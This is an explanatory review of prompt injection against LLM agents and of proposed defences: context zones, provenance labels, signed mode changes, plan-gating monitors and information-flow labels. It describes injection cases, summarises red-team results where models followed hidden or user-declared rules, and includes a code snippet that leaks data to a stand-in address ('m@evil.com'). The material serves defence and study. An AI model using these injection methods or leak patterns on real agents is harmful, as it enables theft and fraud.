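# Design criteria for securing LLM applications: context zones, provenance, signed intent and plan checks

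## LLM applications, prompt injection and the four criteria

A large language model (LLM) is a program that takes in text and predicts how it continues. An LLM application is software that passes text to such a model and uses the output. Early chatbots only displayed that output, but many applications now act on it. The developer gives the model a list of tools, such as functions that send email or query a database, and the software runs the ones named in the model's output. These applications also process a lot of text that their users didn't write, including web pages, incoming mail and shared documents. Anyone who can add words to that text may be able to steer what the application does, which has been called prompt injection since 2022.

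Many early defences were filters that look for bad text entering or leaving the model. In *Unvalidated Trust*, the independent researcher Dominik Schwarz (2025) argued that safety standards may also need criteria for how developers build the whole system. Schwarz listed four: divide the model's context into zones with permissions, record the origin of whatever components pass to each other, require signed intent for a change of mode, and check plans before any tool runs. Schwarz did not test these criteria.

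### From request to tool call

A model keeps no memory between calls, so the software has to supply all the information the model needs each time. The software joins this information into one long text, called the context. It contains the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), descriptions of the available tools, the user's request, earlier turns of the conversation and any documents the software has fetched.

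An agent is an LLM application in which the model chooses tool calls in a loop and reads each result before the next choice. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents*, break the loop into six steps:

1. The agent receives the system prompt and the user's request.
2. The software may fetch relevant documents from a database.
3. The model may reason about a plan, or just about the next step.
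4. The model writes a tool call, which consists of the tool's name and its parameters.
5. The software runs the tool.
6. The result goes into the context, and the loop returns to step 2.

Steps 2 and 3 are optional. Some developers let the model go straight to a tool call, which leaves no written plan to check.

By the second pass, the context holds text from sources that warrant very different levels of trust. Wang and colleagues count the system prompt and the user's request as trusted, tool results as untrusted, and the document database as in between. All of this text sits in a single memory, divided only by textual separators, and the model processes it as one sequence. Nothing in this design gives the user's words a different status, so the model can treat a sentence from a web page as if the user had written it.

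SQL injection, which is nearly 30 years old, exploits a similar confusion between instructions and data. An attacker types database commands into a form field, and the database runs them. Parameterised queries prevent this by fixing the structure of the command first, so that whatever the user types can only be a value. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that no equivalent fix is in sight for language models, because they don't distinguish instructions from data and only predict the next token (a word or piece of a word). Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, attribute the difference to SQL's grammar, which lets a parser tell code from values. Ordinary language has nothing comparable.

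None of this proves that the problem is permanent. Developers can mark external text as data or train models to give it less weight. David C accepts that such methods make attacks harder, but they don't create a boundary.

### Direct and indirect injection

In direct prompt injection, the user is the attacker and puts the hostile instruction in their own message. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker plants instructions in content that the application will read later, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres et al., 2023) introduced indirect prompt injection and demonstrated it against Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant at the time. Bing Chat could read the page the user had open in the browser, and instructions on that page affected the model even when the user couldn't see them.

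Greshake and colleagues also describe emailing the instructions to an assistant that processes the inbox, so the attacker does not have to wait for a visit. Other methods they describe are hiding the instructions in an image and planting a short instruction to fetch a longer one from elsewhere. An email assistant that can both read and send mail could spread an attack from one inbox to the next, like a computer worm. David C gives a simpler example, in which a job applicant hides text in a CV instructing the recruiter's model to approve it for interview.

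The distinction between direct and indirect prompt injection is less clear when users paste text from elsewhere. An attacker can get a user to copy malicious instructions from a web page into a chat, where they become part of the user's own message. Any defence that treats all user input as trusted will also trust those instructions.

### Why a filter on the final answer comes too late

For example, a small firm might have an assistant that can read the mailbox, look things up in the accounts and make bank transfers, each of which a manager has to approve. A user asks it to summarise the week's supplier emails and pay one invoice that is already in the accounts. In one of the emails, an attacker posing as the supplier gives a new account number and says the firm has switched approvals off.

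That email contains two kinds of attack. The line about approvals is meant to change a rule. The account number is a false fact rather than an instruction. Because a payment requires an account number, a model that ignored every command in every email could still pay the wrong account.

Suppose the agent falls for both and sends the transfer at step 5. The model writes its reply only after the loop has finished, summarizing the emails and noting that it has paid the invoice. A filter on that reply runs after the money has left, and would probably pass the text anyway because it contains nothing offensive or secret.

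Moving the filter to the tool call fixes the timing but not the other problem. A transfer to the attacker looks much like a transfer to the supplier, and is wrong because the attacker chose the account number. Narisetty and colleagues call injection against agents with tools an authorisation problem rather than a content problem. To catch it, the software has to know where the account number came from and whether that source was allowed to supply it.

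Schwarz also argues against filters in *Countermind* (2025), a companion design, on the grounds that a hostile input may already have compromised the model's internal state by the time a filter sees the output. This may be true, but *Countermind* is a conceptual design with an evaluation plan and no results. The case for acting before the tool call doesn't depend on this argument. Schwarz proposes the four criteria as additions to output checks, not replacements for them.

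### What the four criteria ask for

The four criteria come from a short paragraph on safety standards in section 12.4 of *Unvalidated Trust*. The seven defence principles in section 10 describe what would enforce them, though they fit some criteria better than others.

The first criterion is "context zoning with permissions". Schwarz would divide the session's memory into zones with explicit privileges, save a new version with a record of its origin at every write, and stop text in an untrusted zone from overriding instructions in a more trusted one. The software that assembles the context and manages memory would do this at steps 1 and 2, and again whenever a tool result comes back at step 6. In the example, the supplier emails would go into a zone that the model may summarise but may not use as a source of rules or payment details. If the zones are only headings inside the prompt, they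 are textual separators again, and the model may ignore them. Software outside the model has to enforce them, for instance by withholding the transfer tool while the emails are in the context.

"Provenance on inter-component exchanges" means that whatever passes from one part of the application to another carries a label for where it came from and how far to trust it. Schwarz worries that text can gain trust by accident, as when one component extracts text from an image and the next treats it as the user's request, though nobody decided to trust it. The sending component must attach the label and the receiving one must check it at every handover, especially when a tool result enters the context and when a tool call leaves the model. The new account number would then reach the transfer tool still labelled as coming from an incoming email, and the tool would refuse it. The user could phone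 the supplier and then override the refusal by deciding to trust the number for this one payment, a step known as endorsement. The hard part is keeping the label attached once the model has rewritten the text, and researchers have worked out formal rules for this.

Of the four criteria, "signed intent for mode transitions" gets the least explanation. None of the seven principles covers it by itself, and the nearest is a requirement to authenticate system prompts against modification. A mode transition can be read as a change in what the application may do, such as from read-only to write access or from asking approval to acting alone. On this reading, the change takes effect only with a cryptographically verifiable statement from someone authorized to order it. A small verifier outside the model would check the signature at the moment of the switch, before the next tool call runs. The model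 must not hold the signing key, because an injected instruction could then make it sign. The attacker's line about approvals has no signature, so approvals stay on. The signature check doesn't catch the false account number, though, and the manager asked for approval may still grant it.

The last criterion is "monitors that gate plan formation before any tool access". The monitor sits between the model's reasoning at step 3 and the first tool call at step 4. Under the matching principle, Schwarz wants the monitor to check plans for hidden commands, with further checks on each tool call and each write to memory. For the firm's assistant, the monitor would approve a plan to read the emails, summarise them, and pay the invoice to the account on file. A later transfer to any other account would fall outside that plan.

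This works because the user's request fixes every step in advance, but requests often leave some steps open. Reading the emails is a tool call, so a plan made before any tool access cannot take account of their contents. If the user had asked the assistant to deal with whatever the suppliers wanted, the gate would have had to approve a very vague plan or block the job. Wang and colleagues call such jobs context-dependent tasks and found that many existing defences overlook them.

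The criteria also depend on each other. Without a provenance label, a gate checking a plan that includes "pay account 4417" can't distinguish the supplier's account number from an attacker's, and a zone's permissions give little protection if an unsigned sentence can change them. Schwarz leaves open whether the criteria work in practice. The experiments in *Unvalidated Trust* measured how models without tools respond to manipulative text, and Schwarz explicitly makes no quantitative claim for any specific control.

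### Two ideas from the 1970s

Much of this is old security doctrine applied in a new setting. In 1972 James Anderson's firm studied how people with different clearances could share one computer, working for the US Air Force with a panel of experts chaired by E. L. Glaser. The panel assumed that a legitimate user might be hostile, so keeping outsiders out would not be enough. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) described a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use another program, a file or a device against a list of what the user may do. The mechanism must be tamper-proof, run on every access, and be small enough to analyse and test completely.

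The conditions were meant to rule out inadequate systems. Anderson applied them to GCOS III, a Honeywell operating system, and it failed. Its memory checks stopped whenever the system acted on a user's behalf, and its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were far too many to verify.

By the same test, a language model cannot be the reference monitor for its own tool calls. It is far larger than GCOS III, and an attacker can write part of its input. A second model that screens the first has the same weakness because, as Narisetty and colleagues point out, an attacker can inject instructions into it too. A plan gate that uses another LLM to judge whether the plan looks suspicious therefore could not qualify as a reference monitor, though it might still catch a fair number of attacks. A signature verifier could qualify, and so could a short program that compares each transfer with a list of approved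 accounts.

The other idea is least privilege. Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) that every program and user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". They had in mind cases like an airline reservation agent who can book and cancel seats but cannot print the full passenger list.

Under this principle, an LLM assistant that only summarises email should not have a transfer tool. The firm's assistant is harder to restrict because its job includes making a payment. The developer could split the job into one run that reads the emails but has no access to the bank, and another that pays the invoice but never sees the emails. David C relays a rule of thumb, from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that leads to the same design. The rule is that when a model processes text from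 some party, its privileges drop to that party's level. A model reading a stranger's email therefore can't make transfers, because the stranger isn't allowed to make them.

Another of Saltzer and Schroeder's principles applies to the approval step. A lock that needs two keys, held by different people, is safer than a lock with one, because a single deception is not enough to open it. They made only modest claims for all of their principles, which they thought served best as warnings.

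### AgentDojo, the common yardstick

Much of the experimental evidence on these ideas comes from one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four workplaces, each with its own data, tools, user tasks and attack goals. The agent's tool calls change the simulated mailbox or bank account. Each user task is paired with every attack goal in the same workplace, so 97 tasks and 27 goals produce 629 security cases.

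| Suite | Tools | User tasks | Attack goals | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel (hotels, flights, cars) | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 |

The banking suite is similar to the supplier example. One of its user tasks is to pay a bill in a text file, and one of its attack goals is to send as much money as possible to the attacker. The attack text goes in places where outsiders could plausibly write and where the agent will look during its task.

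Attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal. Utility is the share of the user's own tasks that the agent completes. Debenedetti and colleagues measure utility both without an attack and under attack, where a case counts only if the agent completes the task without harmful side effects. They score each case with ordinary code that inspects the state of the simulated workplace, for instance to see whether a transfer went out. They avoided using an LLM as judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge.

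The attack success rate and the share of tasks solved need to be read together, because an agent that refuses every request has an attack success rate of zero and is useless. Weak models can also look safe because they often fail at the attacker's task even when they try to carry it out. This partly explains why the more capable models tended to be easier to attack in the first experiments. Those experiments used 2024 models, the best of which solved fewer than 66% of the tasks with no attack present. Attacks succeeded against the best-performing agents in fewer than 25% of cases, and adding a detector for injected text lowered this to 8%.

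AgentDojo is still widely used, though not always in the same form. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) covers 13 models on all four suites, while *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (2025) concentrates on banking. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900 task and attack combinations. Two percentages from AgentDojo therefore don't necessarily have the same denominator.

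The attacker's goals in AgentDojo are written as instructions to the agent. The attacker's line about approvals is somewhat similar, but a false account number in an otherwise ordinary email is not an instruction, so a defence could score perfectly on all 629 cases and still let the agent pay that account. Debenedetti and colleagues also meant the benchmark to grow, with new attacks written against each new defence. Narisetty and colleagues complain that most developers of tool-level defences have instead taken their headline figures from a fixed set of attacks that predate the defence.

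## Model behaviour without architectural controls

Schwarz arrived at the four criteria by testing language models without adding any such controls. The tests ran from 20 August to 10 September 2025 on three commercial models: DeepSeek's deepseek-v3.2-exp-chat, Google's gemini-2.0-flash and OpenAI's gpt-4o. Schwarz also ran Phi-3-mini, a small open model, offline to check how formatting and invisible characters affect how text splits into tokens.

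The outcome was a catalogue of 41 "risk patterns", ways for text to steer a model towards something nobody openly asked for. Schwarz marks 32 of them as empirical, but no benchmark supports one of these, which covers malicious software that rewrites a prompt before it leaves the user's computer.

### How the tests worked

Every test used only text input and output. Schwarz kept the providers' default settings, enabled no tools, browsing or file uploads, and began each trial in a new session. Single-message tests generally had 100 trials per model, while tests that needed a conversation had 50 because they cost more to run. Where a pattern depended on another component, such as software that reads text from an image, the prompt contained the text that component would have produced.

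There are five measures:

- DS (decode success): the model worked out the hidden or disguised request.
- IEO (interpretation escalation output): the model went beyond understanding the request and wrote code or a concrete plan that carries it out.
- POB (policy-override behaviour): the model in effect gave itself permission to do something its policies restrict.
- PDI (policy deviation or inconsistency): the model departed from its expected safety behaviour, for instance by giving contradictory reasons, without necessarily producing anything harmful.
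- RR (refusal or safe redirect): the model understood the request and declined it.

IEO is the main measure, but its meaning varies between tests. One test requires code that would send private files to an outside address, while another requires only the product of two nine-digit numbers, as a harmless sign that the model followed a hidden instruction. POB often adds no information, because most tests record it automatically whenever IEO occurs. In a test about data files, POB requires the model's code to include extras such as error handling or a timeout, which most programmers would call good practice.

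It is also unclear who did the scoring. According to the methods section, two reviewers labelled at least a fifth of the trials in each experiment, but the limitations section describes the scoring as programmatic and gives no figure for agreement between reviewers. However, Schwarz fixed the scoring rules in advance, which makes it harder to choose a flattering definition afterwards.

### What the models did

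These are the IEO rates for the six tests that bear most directly on the criteria:

| Test | DeepSeek | Gemini | GPT-4o | Trials per model |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hidden context seeding | 100% | 74% | 100% | 100 |
| Instruction in a disabled block of code | 53% | 28% | 0% | 100 |
| Triggers in data structures | 100% | 100% | 99% | 100 |
| Premise planted in the model's reasoning | 95% | 97% | 90% | 100 |
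| Session-scoped rule injection | 32% | 100% | 0% | 50 |
| Delayed activation | 6% | 2% | 2% | 50 |

The hidden context seeding test supports the use of context zones. The prompt contained a C++ program with an instruction hidden in its comments. The task was only to analyse the file, yet DeepSeek and GPT-4o wrote steps or code that followed the hidden instruction in every trial. None of the models refused. Schwarz proposes that a parser should separate comments from code before either reaches the model, and mark the comments as untrusted.

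The wording of the prompt matters a great deal, though. In another test, the comments contained an instruction in leetspeak, which replaces letters with digits. All three models understood it in all 100 trials, but none acted on it. The 100% figures therefore describe one prompt and may not hold for other instructions placed in the comments.

The case for provenance labels rests partly on a test that asked models to write a Python script to process a JSON file. One field in the file, `on_startup_hook`, held a shell command, and in 299 of 300 trials the models wrote code that would run it. Schwarz interprets this as data turning into an instruction without anyone deciding to trust it. But a field with that name would normally hold something to run at startup, and many human programmers might have written the same script. A label would help here by showing whoever runs the script that the command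 came from a file of unknown origin.

A test with Base64, a standard way of encoding text as letters and digits, gives cleaner evidence because it had a control. Schwarz encoded a sentence and presented it as a riddle to decode. DeepSeek went beyond decoding in 35 of 100 trials, GPT-4o in 24 and Gemini in 8 (PDI rates). When the same sentence appeared inside a code-analysis task, none of them did so in a combined 300 trials. The models could read the sentence in both cases, so the task changed whether they treated it as something to act on. With a provenance label, this would not depend on the model, because decoded text would keep the trust level of the message it came from.

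#### Rules that a user declares

Session-scoped rule injection is the closest of these tests to an unauthorised mode change. In the first turn, the user declares a rule that supposedly grants special privileges, such as a made-up parameter that allows restricted output. The user ties the rule to an innocent keyword and tells the model to keep it for the whole session. The keyword appears in a later turn, and the trial counts as IEO if the model then writes code that would read a sensitive file and send it elsewhere. Finally, the user asks the model to delete the rule.

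Gemini accepted the rule and produced the code in all 50 sessions. GPT-4o did neither in any session. DeepSeek never agreed to keep the rule, but it still produced the code in 16 sessions. It explicitly refused in 14. A model's statement about which rules are in force can therefore be wrong, so an application with a mode switch needs to store the current mode outside the model.

Schwarz also ran a harmless version, in which the keyword was meant to trigger a "Hello World" program. All three models wrote the program in all 50 sessions, although GPT-4o had explicitly accepted the rule in only 17. GPT-4o can therefore carry an instruction over to a later turn. Its score of zero in the sensitive version is more likely due to the content of the rule than to any general protection against users setting rules.

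With 50 sessions, chance alone could move DeepSeek's 32% quite a bit. A Wilson interval gives the range of underlying rates that fit an observed count reasonably well. For a proportion p = 0.32, n = 50 trials and z = 1.96 (the value for 95% confidence), the calculation is:

(p + z²/2n ± z√(p(1 − p)/n + z²/4n²)) / (1 + z²/n) = (0.358 ± 0.135) / 1.077

The interval runs from 20.8% to 45.8%. It is wide, but far from Gemini's 50 out of 50 and GPT-4o's 0 out of 50, so the three models did differ on this prompt. The interval accounts only for chance variation between runs, not for different wording, a later version of the model or an attacker who tries harder.

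The disabled block of code also resembles a mode change. A build setting disabled the block, which contained a note about a testing mode with the multiplication task. DeepSeek gave the product in 53 trials, Gemini in 28 and GPT-4o in none. DeepSeek and Gemini sometimes went further, for example by proposing to turn the setting on. Neither test involved a signature, but they show that some models accept a change of rules from text with no authority behind it, which is the problem signed intent is meant to solve.

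#### Plans and delayed triggers

The test most relevant to plan checks planted a false premise in the model's written reasoning. The prompt presented a rule as the model's own internal thought, claimed an exception for education, and asked for a phishing email to use in training. The models adopted the premise in their reasoning in at least 92 of 100 trials and usually wrote the email, always with a warning. Under a stricter standard requiring a high-quality email ready for use, the rates fell to 43% for DeepSeek, 26% for Gemini and 10% for GPT-4o.

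The planted premise may have contributed little. In a separate test, a request that merely misspelled "phishing" produced a phishing template in 77% to 99% of trials, depending on the model, so the models were evidently quite willing to write such emails without the premise. The planted-premise test still exposes a weakness in plan gates that read the model's reasoning. Such a gate would have been given a fluent justification for each email, so it is safer to judge the proposed actions than the reasons given for them.

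Delayed activation worked far less often. The first message hid a directive to look for SSH keys, which are files that let someone log in to other computers. A later, neutral message asked for code. DeepSeek wrote code to find the keys in 3 of 50 sessions, and Gemini and GPT-4o in 1 each. Most attempts failed because the models didn't decode the directive. DeepSeek decoded it 7 times, Gemini twice and GPT-4o once. Schwarz writes that GPT-4o has a high probability of producing the code once it has decoded the directive, but this rests on a single session, which gives almost no information about the true rate (the Wilson interval for 1 out of 1 is 20.7% to 100%).

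### From the findings to the seven principles

Schwarz groups the results into three underlying faults, each with a matching remedy. In "trust inheritance", one component accepts another's output without checking it, and the remedy is provenance checks between components. In "interpretation-driven assembly", the model pieces together a request nobody stated and treats it as the task, and the remedy is monitoring the model's reasoning. The third fault is that text from early in a conversation can control what the model does later, and the remedy is dividing memory into zones with privileges.

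These remedies expand into seven principles, each with a list of supporting experiments. The table gives one experiment for each principle.

| Principle | One supporting experiment | DeepSeek / Gemini / GPT-4o |
|---|---|---|
| P1: provenance and no automatic trust between components | A command implied only by the structure of the text | 36% / 18% / 7% (strict scoring) |
| P2: decode in a restricted stage, then check again | Base64 presented as a riddle | 35% / 8% / 24% (PDI) |
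| P3: monitor intermediate reasoning | A request for keylogging code spread across the letters of another text | 81% / 11% / 7% |
| P4: versioned memory with zones | Session-scoped rule injection | 32% / 100% / 0% |
| P5: restrict tools and outputs in sensitive situations | A file-deletion routine written as a poem | 100% / 100% / 100% |
| P6: checks before plans, tool calls and memory writes | Delayed activation | 6% / 2% / 2% |
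| P7: several independent checks | The poem and the spread-out letters | As for P5 and P3 |

The evidence for the principles is uneven. The experiments listed as the basis for P1 include one on invisible characters, which succeeded under strict scoring in 7% of trials with DeepSeek and never with the other two models. Another, on text read from images, has no IEO rate in the summary of results. The JSON test would have been a stronger basis, and Schwarz connects it to P1 elsewhere. P6, the principle closest to a plan gate, relies on two conversations about rules and hidden directives in which no model could call a tool.

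Schwarz describes the principles as "evidence-backed requirements, not speculative best practices". The experiments show that models often acted on text that should have had no authority, but they don't establish that these principles are the right remedy. Several remedies would fit that finding, including better training, and GPT-4o resisted the sensitive session rule even though the tester had added no signature scheme.

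The main argument that the proposed controls are workable rests on differences between models. Schwarz reasons that if the same prompt succeeds every time on Gemini and never on GPT-4o, hardening at particular points in a provider's system must be able to suppress the problem. But nobody switched a control on or off in these tests, and the providers' internal systems were not visible. The difference could come from training, a filter or some quirk in how each model processes the prompt. Evidence for zones or provenance labels specifically would require running one model with and without them.

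Schwarz proposes an experiment that would measure a baseline, then enable each principle alone and in selected combinations, and include attacks that adapt to the defence. The accompanying coverage map lists the expected effect on each measure. For instance, zones should reduce POB when a user tries to plant a rule. Schwarz does not claim that any of the controls works.

The study also has no measurements of agents. One of its scenarios resembles the supplier example: a mailbox assistant receives an email containing a hidden instruction, and when a genuine payment request arrives later, the assistant changes the account field and marks it as verified. The scenario is theoretical and assumes that outsiders can get text to the planning model, that the tools carry out whatever plan it produces, and that planted rules persist in memory. An application that requires approval for each payment might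 stop the attack, while in one with broad permissions, even a rare failure could cause a serious loss. Rates from text-only conversations can't show how often either would happen. In many of the tests, the user also typed the hostile text directly, whereas the attacker in the supplier example can only send an email.

### Countermind

*Countermind*, Schwarz's untested companion design, is one possible way to combine the principles. Each text request would travel in an envelope with an expiry time, a number that works only once, and a code computed from the contents and a secret key. The server would reject any altered, expired or repeated request. Images and audio would first pass through a sandbox that scans them for embedded instructions. A tamper-evident log would record every decision.

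The most unusual part would act inside the model, weakening or removing activity (the numbers passing between its layers) that falls outside the topics a policy allows as the model generates each token. If y is all the activity and Py is the part inside the allowed topics, the model continues with αy + (1 − α)Py. Setting α to 0 removes the activity outside those topics, and a higher value keeps more of it. This depends on topics such as "Python code" and "internal systems" occupying separable regions inside the model, and Schwarz leaves finding those regions to future engineering.

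A valid code on the envelope shows only that a client with the key sent the message and that nobody changed it on the way. Hostile text that a user pastes in would still get a valid code. Schwarz plans to measure attack success, wrongly blocked requests and delay.

### Newer models and repeated attempts

The models in Schwarz's study are now old. OpenAI has gone from GPT-4o to GPT-6, and developers have been training models to give less authority to outside text. System cards, the reports that developers publish about a model's tests, are better evidence of current behaviour. They include direct tests of prompt injection, often with results broken down by the number of attempts the attacker gets.

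Prompt injections against Claude Opus 4.5, which Anthropic released in late 2025, succeed more often when the attacker can make more attempts. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives a success rate of 4.7% for a single very strong attack, 33.6% for ten attempts and 63.0% for a hundred. Rival models from the same period had rates as high as 92%.

If each attempt independently had a 4.7% chance of success, an attacker would succeed at least once in ten attempts 38% of the time, and at least once in a hundred attempts 99% of the time. The measured rate is close to this at ten attempts and well below it at a hundred. A likely explanation is that attacks succeeded early in some test cases and never in others. Even the lower rate leaves a mailbox that accepts a hundred emails poorly protected. Narisetty and colleagues conclude that a defence of this kind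 reduces the number of incidents without setting a limit on them.

Sources disagree about what these attacks targeted. Narisetty and colleagues say the figures come from adaptive attacks on coding agents, while The Decoder says they come from a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan. One of Anthropic's system cards lists a Gray Swan benchmark for tool use separately from its adaptive coding tests, which suggests that the two descriptions refer to different evaluations. The Gray Swan benchmark seems the more likely source, given how well the next model did at coding.

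That model was Claude Opus 4.6, whose system card came out in February 2026. According to VentureBeat, attacks in a constrained coding environment failed on all 200 attempts, even without extra safeguards. When the model operated a graphical interface with extended thinking switched on, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, the rate had reached 78.6% without safeguards and was still 57.1% with them. An injection rate for a model therefore doesn't mean much unless it comes with the setting, the number of attempts and whether safeguards were on.

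Results improved during 2026. In June, Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos 5 had the best score so far on an external Gray Swan benchmark for prompt injection. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports an attack success rate of 2.0% for Claude Opus 5 after 15 attempts on a general Gray Swan test, compared with 5.5% for Opus 4.8. Attacks on browser agents running Opus 5 failed in all 129 test scenarios.

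Schwarz had warned of a "paradox of improvement", in which models that are better at working out hidden requests are also more likely to carry them out. The Claude results show that a more capable model can be considerably harder to inject, but they don't rule out the paradox, because Anthropic may have worked on resistance and capability at the same time.

The browser result of 0 successful attacks out of 129 is impressive, but by the same Wilson formula it is consistent with an underlying success rate of up to 2.9%, and that assumes future attacks resemble the tested ones. Anthropic ran the test with its own software, so safeguards around the model may account for part of the result. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) similarly warns, in its discussion of alignment tests, that an absence of observed failures does not establish reliability across settings.

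Even the 2.0% rate would matter at scale. Suppose an attacker sends 15 different emails to each of 1,000 firms whose assistants all run on Opus 5. If the benchmark rate carried over, about 20 of those assistants would follow the attacker's instructions.

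## Proofs about labels and separated components

A proof can cover every attack that fits its assumptions, including ones nobody has thought of yet, while test results such as those for Opus 5 cover only the attacks that somebody ran. The proof doesn't need a theory of how language models work, because researchers assume that the model obeys whatever the attacker writes, then show that the software around it still rules out certain outcomes. Most of this work uses labels attached to data, an idea from the 1970s that underlies both context zones and provenance.

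### Labels and how they combine

An integrity label records how far the software may trust a piece of data, and a confidentiality label records who may learn it. In the simplest scheme, data is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and either public (L, for low) or secret (H, for high). *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, an agent system built at Microsoft that attaches one label of each kind to every message, tool call and tool result. A supplier's email in a firm's mailbox would have the label (U, H), because an outsider wrote it and the correspondence is private.

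An ordering, written ⊑, defines where data may flow. Trusted data can go wherever untrusted data is acceptable, so T ⊑ U. Public data can go wherever secret data is acceptable, so L ⊑ H. The ordering compares pairs part by part, so (T, L) is at the bottom and (U, H) is at the top. (T, H) and (U, L) are between them, and neither is above the other.

When the software combines two pieces of data, the result gets the lowest label that is at or above both of their labels, called their join (⊔). For example, (T, H) ⊔ (U, L) = (U, H), so a text that mixes the firm's accounts with a public web page is both secret and untrusted. A set of labels in which every pair has a join is a join-semilattice, though most papers call it a "lattice". Dorothy Denning published this model in 1976. Purdue University's *Information Flow, Confinement & Covert Channels* describes it as a set of security classes, an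 operator that combines them and a relation for the permitted flows.

Labels can also list people. A confidentiality label of this kind lists who may read the data, and the join of two such labels is their intersection. If the manager and the bookkeeper may read the accounts, and the bookkeeper and the sales assistant may read the emails, only the bookkeeper may read a summary of both. An integrity label of this kind lists everyone who could have written the data, and the join of two is their union.

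It is hard to tell which parts of a language model's context shaped its output, so Costa and colleagues give the output the join of all the labels in the context. This often overstates the danger, but it doesn't understate it as long as the original labels were right.

### Biba's rule for agents

*SPA* (2026), a design for agents that keep information between requests, traces the two kinds of label to two classical models. The Bell–LaPadula model stops secrets from reaching people without clearance. The Biba model stops unreliable data from influencing anything that requires reliable input. Kenneth Biba described it in *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), a MITRE report for the US Air Force.

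In the strict form of Biba's model, a program may not read data below its own integrity level or write to data above it. An email assistant could not work under the read restriction, since most of its input comes from outsiders. Biba also described a "low-water-mark" version, in which the program may read lower-integrity data but drops to that data's level. Narisetty and colleagues apply this version to agents. Once a model has read untrusted data, it may not authorise a high-integrity action such as a payment, and only endorsement through a trusted channel can raise its level again.

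### The supplier email, step by step

The table shows the labels at each step as the firm's assistant looks up the invoice in the accounts, reads the supplier emails and then tries to pay.

| Step | Data | Label of the data | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The user's request | (T, L) | (T, L) |
| 2 | The invoice from the accounts | (T, H) | (T, H) |
| 3 | The supplier emails | (U, H) | (U, H) |
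| 4 | The model's transfer call | (U, H) | Call refused |

Before each consequential tool call, FIDES joins the labels of the call and all its arguments and requires the result to be trusted. The transfer fails this check at step 4. An attempt to switch off approvals would also fail it. A second check, for confidentiality, requires that everyone who will receive the data is allowed to read it.

The integrity check does not depend on the account number, so it would also refuse a transfer to the supplier's real account, because the model chose that account after reading the emails. Older systems had a similar problem with secrecy labels. If someone writing a confidential document looked up a word in an unclassified dictionary, the dictionary became confidential too, and over time most files moved towards the highest secrecy level.

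In this example, the assistant can pay before it reads the emails. The transfer then has the label (T, H) and passes the check, provided the bank may read the payment details. Alternatively, the software can store the emails in a variable that the planning model never reads, and have a second model without tools summarise them. The planning model's context stays at (T, H), so the model can still pay the account on file. A transfer to an account number taken from an email would fail the check.

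In *Countermind*, Schwarz puts retrieved documents in a read-only zone and expects this to prevent the model from treating their text as instructions. Under label theory, a context zone doesn't have to prevent that, because the software restricts what it will do with the output even if the model obeys the documents.

### Noninterference

Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined noninterference in 1982. A system has this property if any two runs whose inputs differ only in their secret parts produce the same public outputs, so an outsider can't learn anything about the secrets by watching those outputs. The integrity version requires any two runs whose inputs differ only in their untrusted parts to produce the same trusted outputs. For the firm, this would mean that the assistant makes the same payments whatever the suppliers write.

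Many useful agents can't satisfy noninterference. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that replies to meeting requests with the user's availability. Its replies depend on private data by design, so it violates noninterference. Costa and colleagues similarly conclude that full noninterference would in effect stop an agent that had read a secret from using any tool with publicly visible effects. They prove a weaker property, explicit secrecy, which covers data the agent passes along directly but not what an observer can infer from its choice of actions.

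### The LLMbda calculus

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) proves a form of noninterference for a whole programming language instead of a single agent. The language, LLMbda, is a lambda calculus (a minimal language built from functions) with added commands that send text to a model, receive the reply, and copy or clear the conversation. The reply can be a program, which the interpreter then runs. Labels in the basic version are subsets of {U, S}, where U means untrusted and S means secret, and the join of two labels is their union.

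Each value carries a label, and so does the conversation. A reply takes the label of the conversation that produced it. The interpreter also keeps a program-counter label, which records the data that influenced which branch is running. This label is meant to catch implicit flows, in which information passes through a decision. For example, after `if x = 1 then y := 1`, y can reveal something about x even though no command copied x into y.

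Implicit flows are easy to miss. Garby and colleagues found one in CaMeL, a defence in which the model writes a program and a special interpreter tracks where its data came from. The leak works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The program then skips the fourth line, so `rich` stays true. It also keeps its public label, because CaMeL raises a variable's label only when it runs an assignment. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is high. LLMbda handles the equivalent case by halting the run whenever a decision based on a secret would change a public conversation.

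#### The theorems

The first theorem is "termination-insensitive", meaning that it allows secrets to affect whether a run finishes, even though halting can itself reveal something. It uses probabilities because a model can give different replies to the same text. For a program run on two inputs that look identical to some observer, let μ and ν be the respective probability distributions over the results that the observer can tell apart. Either may total less than 1, since some runs never finish. The theorem guarantees a third distribution ω, also with a total of at most 1, such that μ ≤ ω and ν ≤ ω for every result.

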